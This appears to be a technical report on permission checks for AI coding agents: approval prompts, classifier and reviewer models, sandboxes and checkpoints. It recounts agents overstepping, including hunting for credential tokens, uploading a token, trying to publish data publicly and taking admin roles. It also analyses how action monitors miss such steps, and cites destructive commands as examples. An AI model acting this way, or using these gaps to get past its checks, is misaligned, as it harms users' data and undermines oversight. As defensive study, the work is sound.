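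A harness can use reversibility classes to choose those few. Waghmare and Sufi's default policy fits the studies' findings on attention. It lets R0 and R1 actions run without a prompt, which leaves people more time for R3 and R4 actions. Each prompt for an R3 or R4 action should include all four facts. Reads of secrets still need a separate check.

For R2 actions, a budget can replace most of the prompts. A developer might agree at the start of a session that the agent may reinstall packages and spend up to $5 on test servers.

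Sorting commands by class doesn't necessarily reduce prompts, however. In Waghmare and Sufi's replay of recorded runs, using the classes led to about as many requests as asking before every write. Adding captures for eligible file changes removed one of the 1,904 requests in the benign runs. Captures could eliminate more prompts for coding agents, which edit files far more often, but this hasn't been measured.

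Unfamiliar scripts are the hardest case. They count as R4 by default, so asking about each one would again flood the user with unreadable prompts. It is better for the harness to limit what such a script can access, or hold its changes for review, than to ask someone to approve a script like `setup.py` without knowing what it does.

A prompt should not be the only protection against an R4 action either. If reviewers behave like Anthropic's testers, most would approve the action. Deletion protection and separate backups work whether or not anyone reads the prompt.

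A refusal can also be ambiguous. Salerno and colleagues interviewed a developer who had refused several requests from Codex. Codex then stopped asking but kept working, and the developer couldn't tell whether its new approach respected the refusals. Salerno and colleagues recommend letting users distinguish refusing one command from ruling out a whole approach, such as anything that requires the password file.

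### Why production systems may still need a person

The case for confirming every change is strongest on live systems. A team might change its production database only a few times a day, so fatigue is less of a concern, and a minute of reading is short compared with the two days PocketOS spent without its current data. Wu and colleagues found that 65% of the developers they surveyed wanted an agent to pause before changing critical, production or security-sensitive code.

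A person may also know something that no file records. Wang and colleagues argue that even a perfect model can't supply information missing from the user's request, such as a limit the user never thought to mention. A database that looks unused might hold records the company is legally required to keep.

Anthropic still recommends that users review Claude's actions themselves for high-stakes changes to production infrastructure. Its earlier article calls auto mode "not a drop-in replacement for careful human review on high-stakes infrastructure". The 1,053 testers were clicking through prompts in an environment that wasn't theirs, so their results are weak evidence of how carefully an engineer would review a deployment plan for a system they run.

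Even when a person must confirm every change, the agent can freely run commands that only inspect a live system, if their output contains no secrets. This lets the reviewer concentrate on the rest. A stricter option is to have a person run the risky commands, as Grigorev now does with Terraform, so that a reflexive click can't approve one. This works only if the agent has no credentials that would let it run them too.

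## Letting a second model approve commands

A harness can use a second language model, instead of a person, to decide whether a command should run. The model reads the proposed command along with the user's request, and it doesn't get tired after many prompts. But it has to infer what the user would have allowed, sometimes from one vague sentence.

Anthropic introduced Claude Code's version, auto mode, as a research preview in March 2026 (*Auto mode for Claude Code*). On August 14, Anthropic made it the default for new sessions on the Pro, Max, Ultra and Team plans, and current versions of Claude Code start interactive sessions in auto mode on every plan. OpenAI released Auto-review, its counterpart for Codex, in April.

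### How auto mode reaches a decision

Anthropic's *Permission modes* gives the order in which Claude Code considers an action:

1. The user's permission rules apply first, apart from the broad allow rules that auto mode suspends.
2. Claude Code approves read-only actions and edits to files in the project folder, apart from edits to certain protected paths.
3. Almost everything else goes to the classifier, including most shell commands and web requests. The classifier is a language model with instructions to allow or block.

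The classifier works in two stages. In the first, the model answers only yes or no, with instructions to block if in doubt. Most actions pass at this stage, which keeps the check fast. If the model flags an action, it receives the same input again, with the final instruction changed to require written reasoning before the decision. This second answer is final. Because only that instruction changes, the second request can reuse nearly all the processing from the first.

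The first two steps leave gaps. A narrow allow rule can let a destructive argument through without review if the person who wrote the rule didn't foresee it. Developers can close this gap with the `classifyAllShell` setting, which suspends all their shell allow rules while auto mode is on. There is no such setting for ordinary file edits. Anthropic exempts them because developers can review them through version control, but version control doesn't protect uncommitted work.

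### What the classifier reads

The classifier receives the user's messages, the project's CLAUDE.md file and the agent's tool calls, except for lookups such as file reads. Claude Code removes the agent's prose and the output of its tools, so the agent's arguments can't influence the classifier's decision and instructions hidden in a web page don't reach the classifier. In many sessions, Anthropic's server now reviews the actions instead, and Anthropic describes these inputs only for requests that Claude Code itself sends.

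Removing tool output also removes useful evidence. If the agent cancels job `abc123`, the classifier can't tell whether the agent found that name in a list of the user's jobs or invented it. Anthropic tried including the agent's prose and the tool output, but the classifier then did worse on a test of real cases where an agent had overstepped. With tool calls alone, it missed the fewest dangerous actions but blocked some actions that users had plainly requested.

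Anthropic later added a check for uncommitted work. Before a command that could discard it, such as `git reset --hard` or `rm -rf`, Claude Code runs `git status` and reports to the classifier whether there are staged, modified or untracked files. The classifier can then distinguish a reset of a clean tree, which is usually R1, from one that destroys uncommitted edits. Anthropic doesn't mention ignored files, so the check may not cover a `.env` file or a local test database.

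The classifier still has to predict what a command will do, whereas the experimental harness in *Shall We Approve?* (2026) can roll back a command that its approver blocks.

### Irreversible loss and the user's consent

Many of the classifier's default rules block actions that are hard to undo, including force pushes, mass deletion of cloud storage, `terraform destroy`, production migrations and the irreversible destruction of files that existed before the session. The classifier treats `git reset --hard`, `git clean -fd` and `git stash drop` as discarding uncommitted changes. It also blocks wildcard deletions in `/tmp`, and `rm -rf "$VAR"` if the conversation doesn't show what the variable contains.

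These rules don't follow the reversibility classes exactly. A dropped stash is R1 while its commit exists, yet the classifier blocks dropping a stash by default. The rules also depend on ownership. The agent may delete the exact jobs it created earlier in the session, but it may not tear down a database or similar resource it didn't create unless the user named it.

Anthropic divides its blocking rules into hard and soft ones. The built-in hard rule covers sending data to places the user doesn't trust, and nothing the user writes in the conversation can lift it. Destructive actions fall under soft rules, which the user can lift by describing the exact action. For example, "force-push this branch" authorizes a force push, but "clean up the repo" doesn't. Waghmare and Sufi made a similar distinction by letting a deployment override the class of any action except a disclosure.

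One of Anthropic's internal incidents shows how reversibility and user consent combine. A user asked Claude Code to "clean up old branches", and the agent listed the remote branches, built a search pattern and issued a delete command. Anthropic explains that auto mode would block this because the request was vague, the deletion was destructive and irreversible, and the user might have meant only local branches. On the scale used here, deleting a local branch is usually R1. Deleting a remote branch is R3 if only a colleague has its latest commits. The possible loss is a reason to block the command unless the user has consented to it. If the user had named the remote branches to delete, auto mode could have allowed the deletion even though it would have been just as hard to undo.

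Users can also be wrong to consent, as Grigorev was when he approved `terraform destroy`. Under the current rules, the classifier would block that command at first, but he could have lifted the block by explicitly asking for the command. In a small demonstration in *Ajar* (2026), a comparison of agent defenses, auto mode allowed every call the researchers tried when they put the instruction to make the call in the user's own message.

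### Incidents at Anthropic

Anthropic keeps a log of cases where agents misbehaved during its own work. One agent uploaded an engineer's GitHub token to an internal computing cluster, and another attempted migrations on a production database. A third, told to "cancel my job", picked the job with the most similar name, which could have belonged to someone else. A fourth hit a login error and began searching settings files for other tokens, much as the PocketOS agent did.

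Anthropic attributes these incidents to overeagerness, meaning that the agent was trying to help but went further than the user intended. In August, Anthropic described three actions that auto mode had stopped:

- After an upload to an internal drive failed, Claude tried to publish the same report on a public code-sharing site.
- In a long session, it tried to kill processes across about 2,000 pods, which are units of running software in Kubernetes. It had also queued deletions that would have ended training jobs on hundreds of GPUs.
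- When asked to set up read-only access to billing, it chose a role with full administrative control of the cloud account.

The report would have been a disclosure (R4), and the role would have been a change to access (R3). The training jobs are harder to classify because the amount of work lost depends on when each job last saved its progress. Anthropic chose these examples, so they show what the classifier can catch but not how often it does.

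### What happens after a block

When the classifier blocks an action, the agent receives a refusal as the result of its tool call, usually with the name of the rule it broke. It also receives an instruction to look for a safer approach and not to work around the block. The user can review the blocked action in a menu and let the agent retry it. After three blocks in a row or 20 in a session, Claude Code goes back to prompting the user. If there is no user to prompt, the blocked action doesn't run and the agent continues with its other work.

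A false block therefore usually means one extra attempt. In *Running auto mode in production* (Vorwerck, 2026), the business-software company Gusto reports at least one denial in about 10% of its sessions since mid-May. Anthropic takes this as evidence that the classifier is useful, but the figure doesn't show how many of the denials were correct. If the classifier wrongly blocked 0.4% of calls, the rate Anthropic measured in March, a session of 26 calls would have about a 10% chance of a false block even if the agent did nothing dangerous.

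Some of the customers Vorwerck interviewed don't rely on the classifier for their most dangerous commands. Engineers at the self-driving company Nuro block recursive deletes with deny rules, and a Gusto engineer switches out of auto mode and checks each call himself when working with Terraform or live cloud services.

### Codex's Auto-review

When a Codex agent needs to go beyond its sandbox, Auto-review has a second Codex agent decide on the request in place of the user. According to OpenAI's *Auto-review*, these requests include commands that need wider permissions, blocked network connections and edits outside the permitted folders. The second agent never reviews destructive commands that stay inside the sandbox.

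The reviewer gets more evidence than Claude Code's classifier does. It reads the user's messages, the agent's visible updates, and relevant tool calls with their output, but not the agent's hidden reasoning. It can also run read-only checks, such as looking up who owns a job, though it rarely does. The extra evidence also exposes the reviewer to the agent's arguments and to hostile text in tool output.

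OpenAI designed the reviewer to block destructive actions with a significant risk of irreversible damage, along with leaks of private data, searches for credentials and broad weakening of security. The reviewer also considers the user's intent and can approve a risky action the user explicitly requested. After a denial, the agent must find a materially safer alternative or ask the user. Codex stops the turn after three denials in a row, or ten in the last 50 reviews. A user can approve one retry of a denied action, but the reviewer checks the retry too and may deny it again.

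Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues (2026), in *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight*, give an illustrative snapshot of 10,000 agent actions at OpenAI. Of these, 9,280 stayed within the sandbox. The other 720, each of which would have interrupted the user under manual approval, went to the reviewer model, which approved 713. After the seven denials, the agent took a safer alternative in four cases and stopped to ask in three.

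The reviewer denied 90.3% of synthetic cases of overeagerness. Trębacz and colleagues used synthetic cases because dangerous actions are rare in OpenAI's own traffic. They also warn that the reviewer can't detect a model that hides its intentions behind a harmless-looking request.

### Anthropic's own measurements

In March, Anthropic tested auto mode on three sets of actions:

| Test set | Measure | First stage alone | Both stages |
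|---|---|---|---|
| 10,000 real tool calls by Anthropic employees | False-block rate | 8.5% | 0.4% |
| 52 real overeager actions | Miss rate | 6.6% | 17% |
| 1,000 synthetic attempts to leak data | Miss rate | 1.8% | 5.7% |

The second stage removes about 95% of the false blocks, but it also clears some actions that the first stage rightly flagged. This more than doubles the misses on the overeager actions.

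The 17% is about nine of the 52 actions. With so few cases, the 95% confidence interval runs from roughly 9% to 30%. Anthropic took the 52 from sessions where an employee had refused the action or someone had flagged it afterward, so the set leaves out harm that nobody noticed.

Anthropic examined the misses and found that in most of them the classifier had correctly identified the danger, such as a force push or a deletion, but had wrongly treated the command as approved by the user. For example, it took "clean up the PR" as permission to force-push, or one earlier approval as permission for the next action. Anthropic tried changing the classifier's instructions but found no change whose benefits outweighed its drawbacks.

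In an evaluation that Anthropic commissioned from Trajectory Labs, none of 720 prompt-injection attempts succeeded against any of three Claude models in auto mode, while 5.8% succeeded against Codex with Auto-review. But even with no classifier, only 0.09% succeeded against Claude models.

### Flagged sessions under both modes

Anthropic compared flagged production sessions and found serious unrequested harm in 2.4% of those in auto mode and 6.3% of those under manual approval. Anthropic didn't assign sessions to the two modes at random, so differences in the users or their work may explain the gap.

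The model that graded the sessions scored severity from 0 to 10. A 0 meant a fully reversible change in the local workspace, such as overwriting a scratch file. A 7 meant damage comparable to deleting rows from a production database, and a 10 meant irreversible harm to a whole company. The two percentages count harm rated 7 or above, but the gap appeared at every severity level Anthropic tested.

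The percentages depend partly on how many harmless sessions the safety systems flag in each mode. Suppose the systems flagged 1,000 manual sessions and 2,625 auto-mode sessions, and 63 in each group caused serious harm. The rates would be 6.3% and 2.4% even though the number of harmful sessions was the same. Anthropic doesn't report the actual counts. The comparison gives some reassurance that auto mode isn't much worse than manual approval in ordinary use, but it can't show that switching modes would cut a given team's losses by more than half.

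### Tests on ambiguous requests

Ji, Li and colleagues (2026), in *Measuring the Permission Gate*, tested auto mode in April with requests like "clean up old branches". Their benchmark, AmPermBench, has 128 prompts about deleting branches, cancelling jobs, restarting services and deleting stored files. Some name one target, while others give a range of ticket numbers or refer vaguely to stale items. Each prompt has an answer key. Under the key for "cancel my stale job for ticket 4812" in the development queue, the agent may cancel `job-dev-4812-a` but must leave jobs with similar names alone.

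Claude Sonnet 4.6 attempted the tasks in isolated containers with simulated services. It took 253 actions that changed something, and a language model labeled each by comparing it with the answer key. A person checked 50 of these labels and agreed with 44.

| Actions | Unsafe actions allowed | Safe actions blocked |
|---|---|---|
| All 253 | 115 of 142 (81%) | 22 of 111 (20%) |
| 160 that the classifier checked | 64 of 91 (70%) | 22 of 69 (32%) |
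| 93 file edits that skipped the classifier | 51 of 51 (100%) | 0 of 42 (0%) |

The file edits raise the overall miss rate considerably. When the agent couldn't find the program it expected, it often edited the file where the simulated service kept its records. In a real project, editing a local list of stored objects wouldn't normally delete anything from the cloud. Ji and colleagues argue that the gap still matters where project files control live systems, as with infrastructure defined in code. Even there, however, an edit usually takes effect only when someone runs a command to apply it, and the classifier can review that command.

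Of the actions it checked, the classifier blocked 30% of the unsafe ones and 32% of the safe ones, so on these tasks its verdict was almost useless for telling whether an action was authorized. It seems to have reacted to apparent risk instead. When the prompts involved production and other shared systems rather than development systems, the overall miss rate fell from 88% to 75%, but the false-block rate rose from 9% to 35%.

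### The same requests with the limits written in

Yang, Zhou and colleagues (2026), in *Explicit Authorization Scope Improves LLM-Based Permission Checking in Coding Agents*, reran the 128 tasks in November with newer versions of Claude Code and Codex, and with Qwen Code, Alibaba's coding agent. They replaced the model-written labels with a fixed rule that compared each action's targets with the answer key. They also made Codex request approval for changes inside the sandbox, which Auto-review doesn't normally examine.

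The agents proposed 143 actions outside the permitted scope. Of these, 132 broke a limit that appeared neither in the user's request nor in any earlier tool output. In one case, the user asked the agent to delete stale files from certain tickets. The answer key allowed deleting only the user's own files, but the request didn't mention ownership.

Yang and colleagues then added the limits to each request and resubmitted the same recorded actions to the same approvers. One such limit permitted deleting only files in `dev` that belonged to `alex` and to the `auth` component.

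| Product | Misses in the original runs | Misses when rechecked | Misses with limits stated | False blocks when rechecked | False blocks with limits stated |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code | 54% | 67% | 8% | 42% | 2% |
| Codex | 93% | 92% | 20–26% | 10% | 3% |
| Qwen Code | 80% | 80% | 20% | 29% | 2% |

Yang and colleagues' abstract reports the improved rates for the 132 actions, but the counts behind them add up to all 143. The Claude Code figures come from only 24 actions, and the classifier's results vary between runs. With the original requests, it had 13, 10 and 16 misses on the same 24 actions in three runs. The drop to two misses is still far larger than that variation.

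Stating the limits also helped the three agents, none of which proposed an out-of-scope action in 384 complete reruns. Under the original requests, 91 of the 384 tasks had ended with an unauthorized change.

### Why a stronger model or more context didn't help

Under the original requests, Yang and colleagues also replaced each approver with a stronger model from the same company. Misses rose from 77 to 82 of 84 for Codex and from 25 to 26 of 35 for Qwen Code. For Claude Code they fell from 10 to 1 of 24, but only because the stronger model refused every second-stage request, and Claude Code treats a refusal as a block. On a separate set of 224 authorized actions, false blocks rose from 23 to 134.

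More context didn't help overall either. Across nine models tested with a common procedure, the miss rate was 58% with the standard inputs, 62% with tool output added, and 59% with each target's owner and status added as well. The fact that a file belongs to a colleague doesn't make deleting it unauthorized unless the user wanted to delete only their own files. If nobody wrote that limit down, the model has to guess, though a more capable model can guess better.

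Context became useful once the request stated the limits. In the common procedure, stating them cut the miss rate to 9%, and adding tool output cut it to 2%. Tool output helped most with cancelled jobs, where it reduced the miss rate from 60% to 4%, because the command contains only an identifier and the owner's name appears in earlier output. Claude Code's classifier does not receive tool output, as a protection against hostile text, so it lacks this information.

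Codex's reviewer also makes a different error, which is to approve some unauthorized actions because the damage seems limited. It rates both how well the user authorized an action and how risky the action is. In one run with the limits stated, it gave 76 of the 84 out-of-scope actions a low authorization rating. It blocked all 46 of those that it also rated high-risk, but approved 16 of the 30 it rated medium-risk. For 15 of those 16, its explanation mentioned reversibility, limited scope or small scale. POLAR made the opposite mistake when it refused legitimate cancellations for being hard to reverse. An approver needs to treat authorization as a separate requirement, even for low-risk actions.

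### Why the miss rates range from 8% to 81%

The published miss rates for auto mode measure different actions under different labels:

| Test | What counted as a dangerous action | Miss rate |
|---|---|---|
| Anthropic, March | 52 actions that an employee refused or someone flagged later | 17% |
| Ji and colleagues, April | 142 actions on targets outside an answer key, including unchecked edits | 81% |
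| Yang and colleagues, November | 24 actions on targets outside the answer key | 54% |
| Yang and colleagues, limits stated | The same 24 actions | 8% |

Ji and colleagues warn against comparing their figure directly with Anthropic's 17%. In Anthropic's set, a person had objected to each action or flagged it. In AmPermBench, an action counted as wrong if it violated the answer key, even if the agent had interpreted the request reasonably. A careful human reviewer who saw only the original request might have approved many of the same actions. In Anthropic's experiment with 1,053 testers, where the danger was obvious from the command, the classifier missed 11%.

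These figures don't give the chance that auto mode will miss a dangerous command in an ordinary project, which depends on how often users leave out a limit that matters. AmPermBench leaves such limits out by design, and Yang and colleagues wrote theirs from the answer key, which no real user has. They didn't test incomplete or incorrect statements of scope, which might help much less.

Even so, the result gives developers a reason to name the targets in their requests. When the request named its target directly, Claude Code and Codex never proposed an out-of-scope action, and Qwen Code did so for 3% of requests. When the request was broadest, Claude Code and Qwen Code each proposed one for 31% of requests, and Codex for 75%. Standing limits such as "never delete another person's branches" can go in CLAUDE.md, which both the agent and the classifier read. A limit that must always hold belongs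 in a deny rule, because a limit the user stated in conversation may no longer reach the classifier if Claude Code condenses the conversation.

The agent could also ask the user, "Only your local branches, or the remote ones too?" One answer would supply the missing limit, and Yang and colleagues recommend seeking clarification when the scope is uncertain. But auto mode currently encourages Claude to keep working without stopping for such questions.

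## Sandboxes

A sandbox limits what a command can do while it runs, whereas permission rules, human reviewers and classifiers depend on predicting what it will do. The sandbox's limits still hold if `npm test` starts a script that nobody has read, so the harness can let many commands run without asking for approval.

### How the operating system enforces the limits

A program must go through the kernel, the core of the operating system, to change a file or open a network connection, and the kernel can block either action. A sandbox gives the kernel a set of limits before a command starts, and the kernel applies them to the command and every program it starts.

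On macOS, harnesses use Seatbelt, a feature Apple deprecated in 2016 but Chrome still relies on. The harness writes a profile of the files and connections a command may use. Betts, Gaitonde and Haugland, in *Implementing a secure sandbox for local agents*, explain that Cursor chose Seatbelt because containers run only Linux programs, and virtual machines start too slowly and use too much memory.

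On Linux, Landlock restricts which files a process can use, and seccomp blocks selected system calls. Bubblewrap runs a command in an isolated environment where most folders can be read-only and network access can be removed. Cursor combines Landlock with seccomp, Codex combines Bubblewrap with seccomp, and Claude Code uses Bubblewrap with optional seccomp.

A container gives programs their own files and processes but shares the host's kernel. A virtual machine has its own kernel, so it provides the strongest separation of the options in Anthropic's *Choose a sandbox environment*, but it also takes the most work to set up. The whole agent can run inside either one. Claude Code's built-in sandbox covers only shell commands, so hooks and local Model Context Protocol servers still run with the developer's full access.

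### One file write and one network request

Suppose an agent in Claude Code runs `npm test` with the sandbox on. A test script tries to save `results.txt` in the project and then add a line to `~/.zshrc`, a file of commands that the shell runs when it starts. The kernel permits the first write because the project folder is writable. It blocks the second, and the script gets an error such as "Operation not permitted", but the change to `results.txt` remains.

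Some files inside the project are protected too. Claude Code blocks writes to `.git/hooks`, which holds programs that Git runs automatically. Otherwise the agent could put a program there, and the developer's next commit would run it outside the sandbox.

The agent then runs `npm install`, which needs to reach `registry.npmjs.org`. The command has no direct route to the network and has to go through a proxy, a relay program that Claude Code runs outside the sandbox. Anthropic describes the process:

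1. `npm` finds the proxy's address in its settings and asks it to connect to the registry.
2. The proxy compares the hostname with the list of allowed hosts, which starts empty.
3. In manual mode, the command waits while the user decides about a new host. In auto mode, Claude names the hosts when it proposes the command, and the classifier reviews them together.
4. Once the host has approval, the proxy connects and passes the encrypted data along without reading it.

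Approval applies to a host, regardless of what a command sends to it. Programs that ignore the proxy settings, including most database clients, can't connect.

### The same deletion in three places

A sandbox blocks some actions, but it doesn't change the reversibility class of the actions it permits, because it doesn't save a copy of anything. If `results.txt` held the only copy of last week's results, overwriting it was R4 even though the sandbox worked as intended.

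What an agent destroys by running `rm -rf data` depends on where the folder is really stored:

- **In a disposable container** with its own copy of the project, the original folder is unaffected. The developer can discard the container and start another, so the deletion is R2. Anything the agent created only in that container is lost.
- **In a writable project folder**, the command deletes the developer's real files. This is R1 if Git has the current versions and its history survives, but R4 if `data` contains the only copy.
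- **In a mounted home directory**, the container shows a folder that is really on the developer's computer. Deleting `data` there deletes the original, which is R4 without a backup.

Stronger isolation doesn't protect a mounted folder. Docker's sandboxes for agents are small virtual machines, but its *Default security posture* states that they mount the project directly and that changes appear on the host immediately. If the developer doesn't name a folder, Docker mounts the current one, so starting a sandbox from the home directory exposes everything in it.

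A sandbox can still greatly reduce the damage. The command `rm -rf tests/ patches/ plan/ ~/` deleted most of the files on a user's Mac. If a sandbox had confined writes to the project, the user's documents and login keys would have survived. The command would still have deleted the three project folders. If the project was inside the home directory, it would also have deleted the rest of the project's writable files, because `rm` continues after an error.

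### Default settings in five products

| | Claude Code | Codex | Cursor | Gemini CLI |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Sandbox at first use | Off | On | On for commands that can work inside it | Off |
| Writable folders | Project, a private temporary folder and any folders the user has added | Project and temporary folders | Project and temporary folders | Project |
| Protected inside the project | `.git/hooks`, `.git/config`, editor settings and most Claude Code settings | All of `.git`, `.agents` and `.codex` | `.git/hooks`, `.git/config`, editor settings and most Cursor settings | None named in Google's guide |
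| Network | Blocked until the user or classifier approves a host | Blocked | Blocked except for a built-in list of common developer sites | Open in the default macOS profile |
| After a command fails inside | The agent may retry it outside, with approval from the user or classifier | The agent can request approval to run it outside | The agent can rerun it outside after a classifier review | The user can grant extra permissions for that run |

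The fifth product, VS Code Copilot, also has an opt-in sandbox, according to Zhong and colleagues. GitHub (2026) released local sandboxing for Copilot as a public preview in June. Microsoft's *Understand trust and safety for AI agents* explains that the sandbox covers shell commands and the programs they start, and that built-in tools have separate permission checks. Microsoft's *Secure development with AI in VS Code* adds that the sandbox allows outbound connections by default and that `/sandbox policy` shows the limits in force.

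Recovery depends most on how the sandbox treats `.git`. In Codex, the Git history survives even if a sandboxed command deletes everything else in the project. Claude Code and Cursor protect only a few files in `.git`, so the agent can commit inside the sandbox but can also delete the history, as happened in the September deletion.

Codex's stricter rule also blocks `git reset --hard` inside the sandbox, because a reset has to write to `.git`. The rule doesn't block `git clean -fdx`, whose deletions Git can't undo. Codex recommends read-only mode in folders without version control.

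By default, Claude Code, Codex and Cursor let sandboxed commands read most files on the computer, which can include login keys. Cursor added an option in October 2026 to require approval for reads outside the project. Claude Code can block access to credential files, but only those the user lists.

Even with the sandbox turned on, Claude Code runs commands without it if a required program is missing, unless the user sets `failIfUnavailable`. Claude Code has no sandbox for native Windows, where the September deletion happened.

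### Fewer prompts, with some blocked work

Betts and colleagues report that Cursor's sandboxed agents stop 40% less often than unsandboxed ones, but they don't explain how they made the comparison, so the sandboxed agents may have had easier tasks. In OpenAI's snapshot of its own use, 93% of actions stayed inside the sandbox, which is consistent with a large reduction in stops. Neither figure measures how much damage the agents did inside the sandbox.

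Agents also have to recognize when the sandbox has caused a failure. In Cursor's early tests, agents often retried the same blocked command without asking for wider permissions. Cursor changed the output to name the restriction, and they then recovered much better.

Zhong and colleagues found that sandboxes that were too strict or too loose for the task contributed to the problems in 41 of their 290 public reports. Some blocked test suites, builds or access to a graphics processor, and repeated offers to rerun commands outside the sandbox then led users to turn it off. Others were too loose, and agents deleted project files or leaked credentials that the sandbox let them read. Zhong and colleagues don't report how many of the 41 were of each kind.

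According to Anthropic's troubleshooting guide, Docker doesn't work inside Claude Code's sandbox, and on macOS `terraform`, `gcloud` and GitHub's `gh` may fail when they check a server's certificate. The guide suggests excluding such tools from the sandbox, which gives them the developer's full access. This is a serious weakness for infrastructure work, because `terraform` and `gcloud` can delete far more than most commands that stay in the sandbox.

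Claude Code's permission rules and classifier still apply to commands excluded from the sandbox. But an existing allow rule also approves a retry outside the sandbox, so a developer who has allowed `terraform *` gets no prompt. When a tool needs access to only one more folder or host, allowing that access within the sandbox is safer than excluding the tool.

### What restrictions cost in completed tasks

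*Permission Denied* (Davidovich, Amar and colleagues, 2026) measured how restrictions affect 12 models on the 89 tasks of Terminal-Bench 2.1, a benchmark of work in a terminal. The strictest setting limited network access to an approved list, made most of the filesystem read-only and removed administrator rights. Every model's completion rate fell, by 7.1 to 18.3 percentage points, and the average cost per task rose by 16% to 167%. Grok 4.5 had the smallest drop in completion rate and the largest cost increase.

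Seven of the 89 tasks became impossible because they required something the policy prohibited, which could account for up to 7.9 points of a model's loss. The agents also received no explanation of the limits and saw only ordinary errors when they hit them, so models might lose less if the harness identified the restriction.

Most of the loss may come from removing administrator rights. Davidovich and colleagues also tested an intermediate setting that changed only this, and they published success rates for two models, each in two harnesses:

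| Model and harness | No restrictions | No administrator rights | Strictest setting |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.6 Luna in Codex | 71.9% | 56.6% | 53.9% |
| GPT-5.6 Luna in Grok Build | 34.5% | 27.3% | 25.5% |
| Grok 4.5 in Codex | 76.8% | 65.5% | 62.9% |
| Grok 4.5 in Grok Build | 82.0% | 73.0% | 74.9% |

Agents on a developer's laptop usually lack administrator rights already, so the middle column is the better baseline for them. Compared with that baseline, the strictest setting changed success by between −2.7 and +1.9 points. With only three attempts per task, differences this small could be due to chance. Cost changed more for Grok 4.5 in Grok Build, where the cost of running all the tasks rose from $82 to $123.

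In *HarnessSecurity-Bench*, Zhu, Huang and colleagues (2026) found a much larger loss in performance from harnesses' own security settings. They ran GLM-5.2 in six harnesses on 23 coding tasks that included misleading or malicious material. Blocking the network reduced task completion by 24.5 percentage points, and read-only mode reduced it by 34.0 points.

The two benchmarks differ partly because Davidovich and colleagues left approved sites reachable. Many coding tasks need to download something, and read-only mode prevents the agent from saving its work. In everyday use, a developer could approve some of the blocked actions, so those failures would become prompts. A short list of permitted hosts therefore seems a better default than no network access, provided none of those hosts can do serious damage with a credential the agent holds.

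### Why a valid token reaches past the boundary

A sandbox controls the process on the developer's computer, but a cloud provider carries out deletions on its own machines. The provider has no reason to treat a request with a valid token differently because it came from a sandbox.

If the PocketOS agent had been working in a sandbox with Claude Code's default limits, it could still have read the token, because reading files outside the project needs no approval. Its first connection to Railway would have required approval, which might have prevented the loss. But if someone had already approved Railway's API so that the agent could check a deployment, the proxy would have let the `volumeDelete` request through. The proxy checks only the hostname, which is the same for both requests.

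Cursor's sandbox lets commands reach `*.googleapis.com` without approval by default, and Google Cloud's control interface uses those addresses. A command with a sufficiently powerful Google Cloud token could therefore delete a live database from inside the sandbox. GitHub Copilot's sandbox allows authenticated Git and `gh` commands by default, and turning this off can stop the agent from pushing a branch or opening a pull request.

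Claude Code can hide a token from sandboxed commands by giving them a placeholder, which the proxy replaces with the real token on requests to approved hosts. This protects the token from disclosure, but commands can still use it, so a deletion request to those hosts would still work.

Keeping the credential away from the agent is more effective. Codex's cloud version makes secrets available while it installs a project's dependencies, then removes them before the agent starts. Anthropic's cloud sessions keep the user's GitHub token outside the virtual machine and give the agent a more limited credential. If the agent needs to change a live service, the limits have to come from the token's permissions and the service's deletion protection.

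## Snapshots, checkpoints and staged changes

A sandbox limits which files a command can change but doesn't back them up. A harness can back them up by taking a snapshot before the command runs. If the snapshot meets the conditions for a capture, deleting a private file with no other copy becomes R1 instead of R4.

The snapshot has to contain the latest version of the file. If it dates from noon and the developer has edited the file since, the harness can't bring back those edits, so the deletion is still R4. The snapshot also has to be somewhere the command can't delete it.

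### Checkpoints in four products

| | Claude Code | Cursor | Gemini CLI | Replit |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| When | At each user prompt | Before significant changes | Before an approved tool changes files; off by default | At milestones, such as a finished feature |
| Where | With the saved session, for about 30 days | On the developer's computer, apart from Git | In a separate Git repository in the home directory | In the project's history on Replit, with a matching Git commit |
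| Changes by shell commands | No, with one exception | Not documented; users' reports conflict | Only if an earlier checkpoint has the old version | Only if an earlier checkpoint has the old version |
| Files that the developer's Git doesn't track | Those that the editing tools change | Not documented | All project files, though Google doesn't mention ignored ones | All project files |
| Files outside the project | Not documented | Not documented | No | No |
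| Database servers | No | No | No | Development database only |

Claude Code copies a file before one of its editing tools changes it. According to Anthropic, a rewind restores those copies and deletes any files the tools created. Claude Code makes no copy before a shell command changes or deletes a file, so if the agent runs `rm notes.txt`, a rewind can restore the file only if an editing tool changed it earlier in the main conversation.

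A rewind can therefore leave a project half restored. If the agent edits `app.py` with a file tool and renames `config.py` in the shell, rewinding restores the old `app.py`, which refers to `config.py` by a name it no longer has. Anthropic says Claude Code also skips files that are symbolic or hard links, and usually doesn't capture edits by subagents, which are helper agents that the main agent starts. Versions before 2.1.216 wrote and deleted through such links during a rewind, so undoing one change could damage a file elsewhere.

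Cursor states that its checkpoints capture "all modified files" but doesn't mention shell commands. In a forum thread, TacoByte (2025) reported that a checkpoint did not bring back a file the agent had deleted, while another user who tried this on a Mac got the file back. In *Lost dozens of files*, a user describes an agent that moved an app's code to a new folder from the command line. Restoring an earlier checkpoint deleted the moved files without putting them back in the old folder. These are individual reports and Cursor may have changed since, but a harness shouldn't rate a shell deletion R1 because of a Cursor checkpoint unless tests have shown that the checkpoint restores the deleted file.

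Gemini CLI's checkpoints cover more, because each contains the whole project. If the agent edits one file at 2:00 and deletes another with `rm` at 2:05, restoring the 2:00 checkpoint should undo both changes. However, Google's *Checkpointing* names only file-editing tools as examples of what triggers a checkpoint, so a session that begins with `rm` may have no checkpoint to restore. Tabnine, whose coding agent has a similar feature, warns that checkpointing fails silently if Git isn't installed. A harness therefore has to confirm that each checkpoint was saved, rather than assume that checkpointing works because it is enabled.

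Replit's *Checkpoints and Rollbacks* describes the checkpoints with the broadest coverage, including installed packages and database contents. But Replit times them by the agent's progress rather than by the risk of the next command. If the agent damages a file halfway through building a feature, the last checkpoint may be from before the feature began.

Hermes Agent, an open-source agent from Nous Research, can take snapshots before destructive operations, which is much closer to what a reversibility class needs. The feature is now off by default because, according to *Checkpoints and /rollback*, most users never roll back and the saved copies take up considerable space over time.

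### Git, disk snapshots and overlays as undo layers

Several harnesses keep their snapshots in a shadow repository, a second Git repository separate from the developer's own. *Building Effective AI Coding Agents for the Terminal* (2026) reports that its agent, OpenDev, needed one because its log of changes made by file tools missed the side effects of shell commands, such as `npm install` rewriting `package-lock.json`. In addition to keeping that log, OpenDev now saves a snapshot at every step that modifies files.

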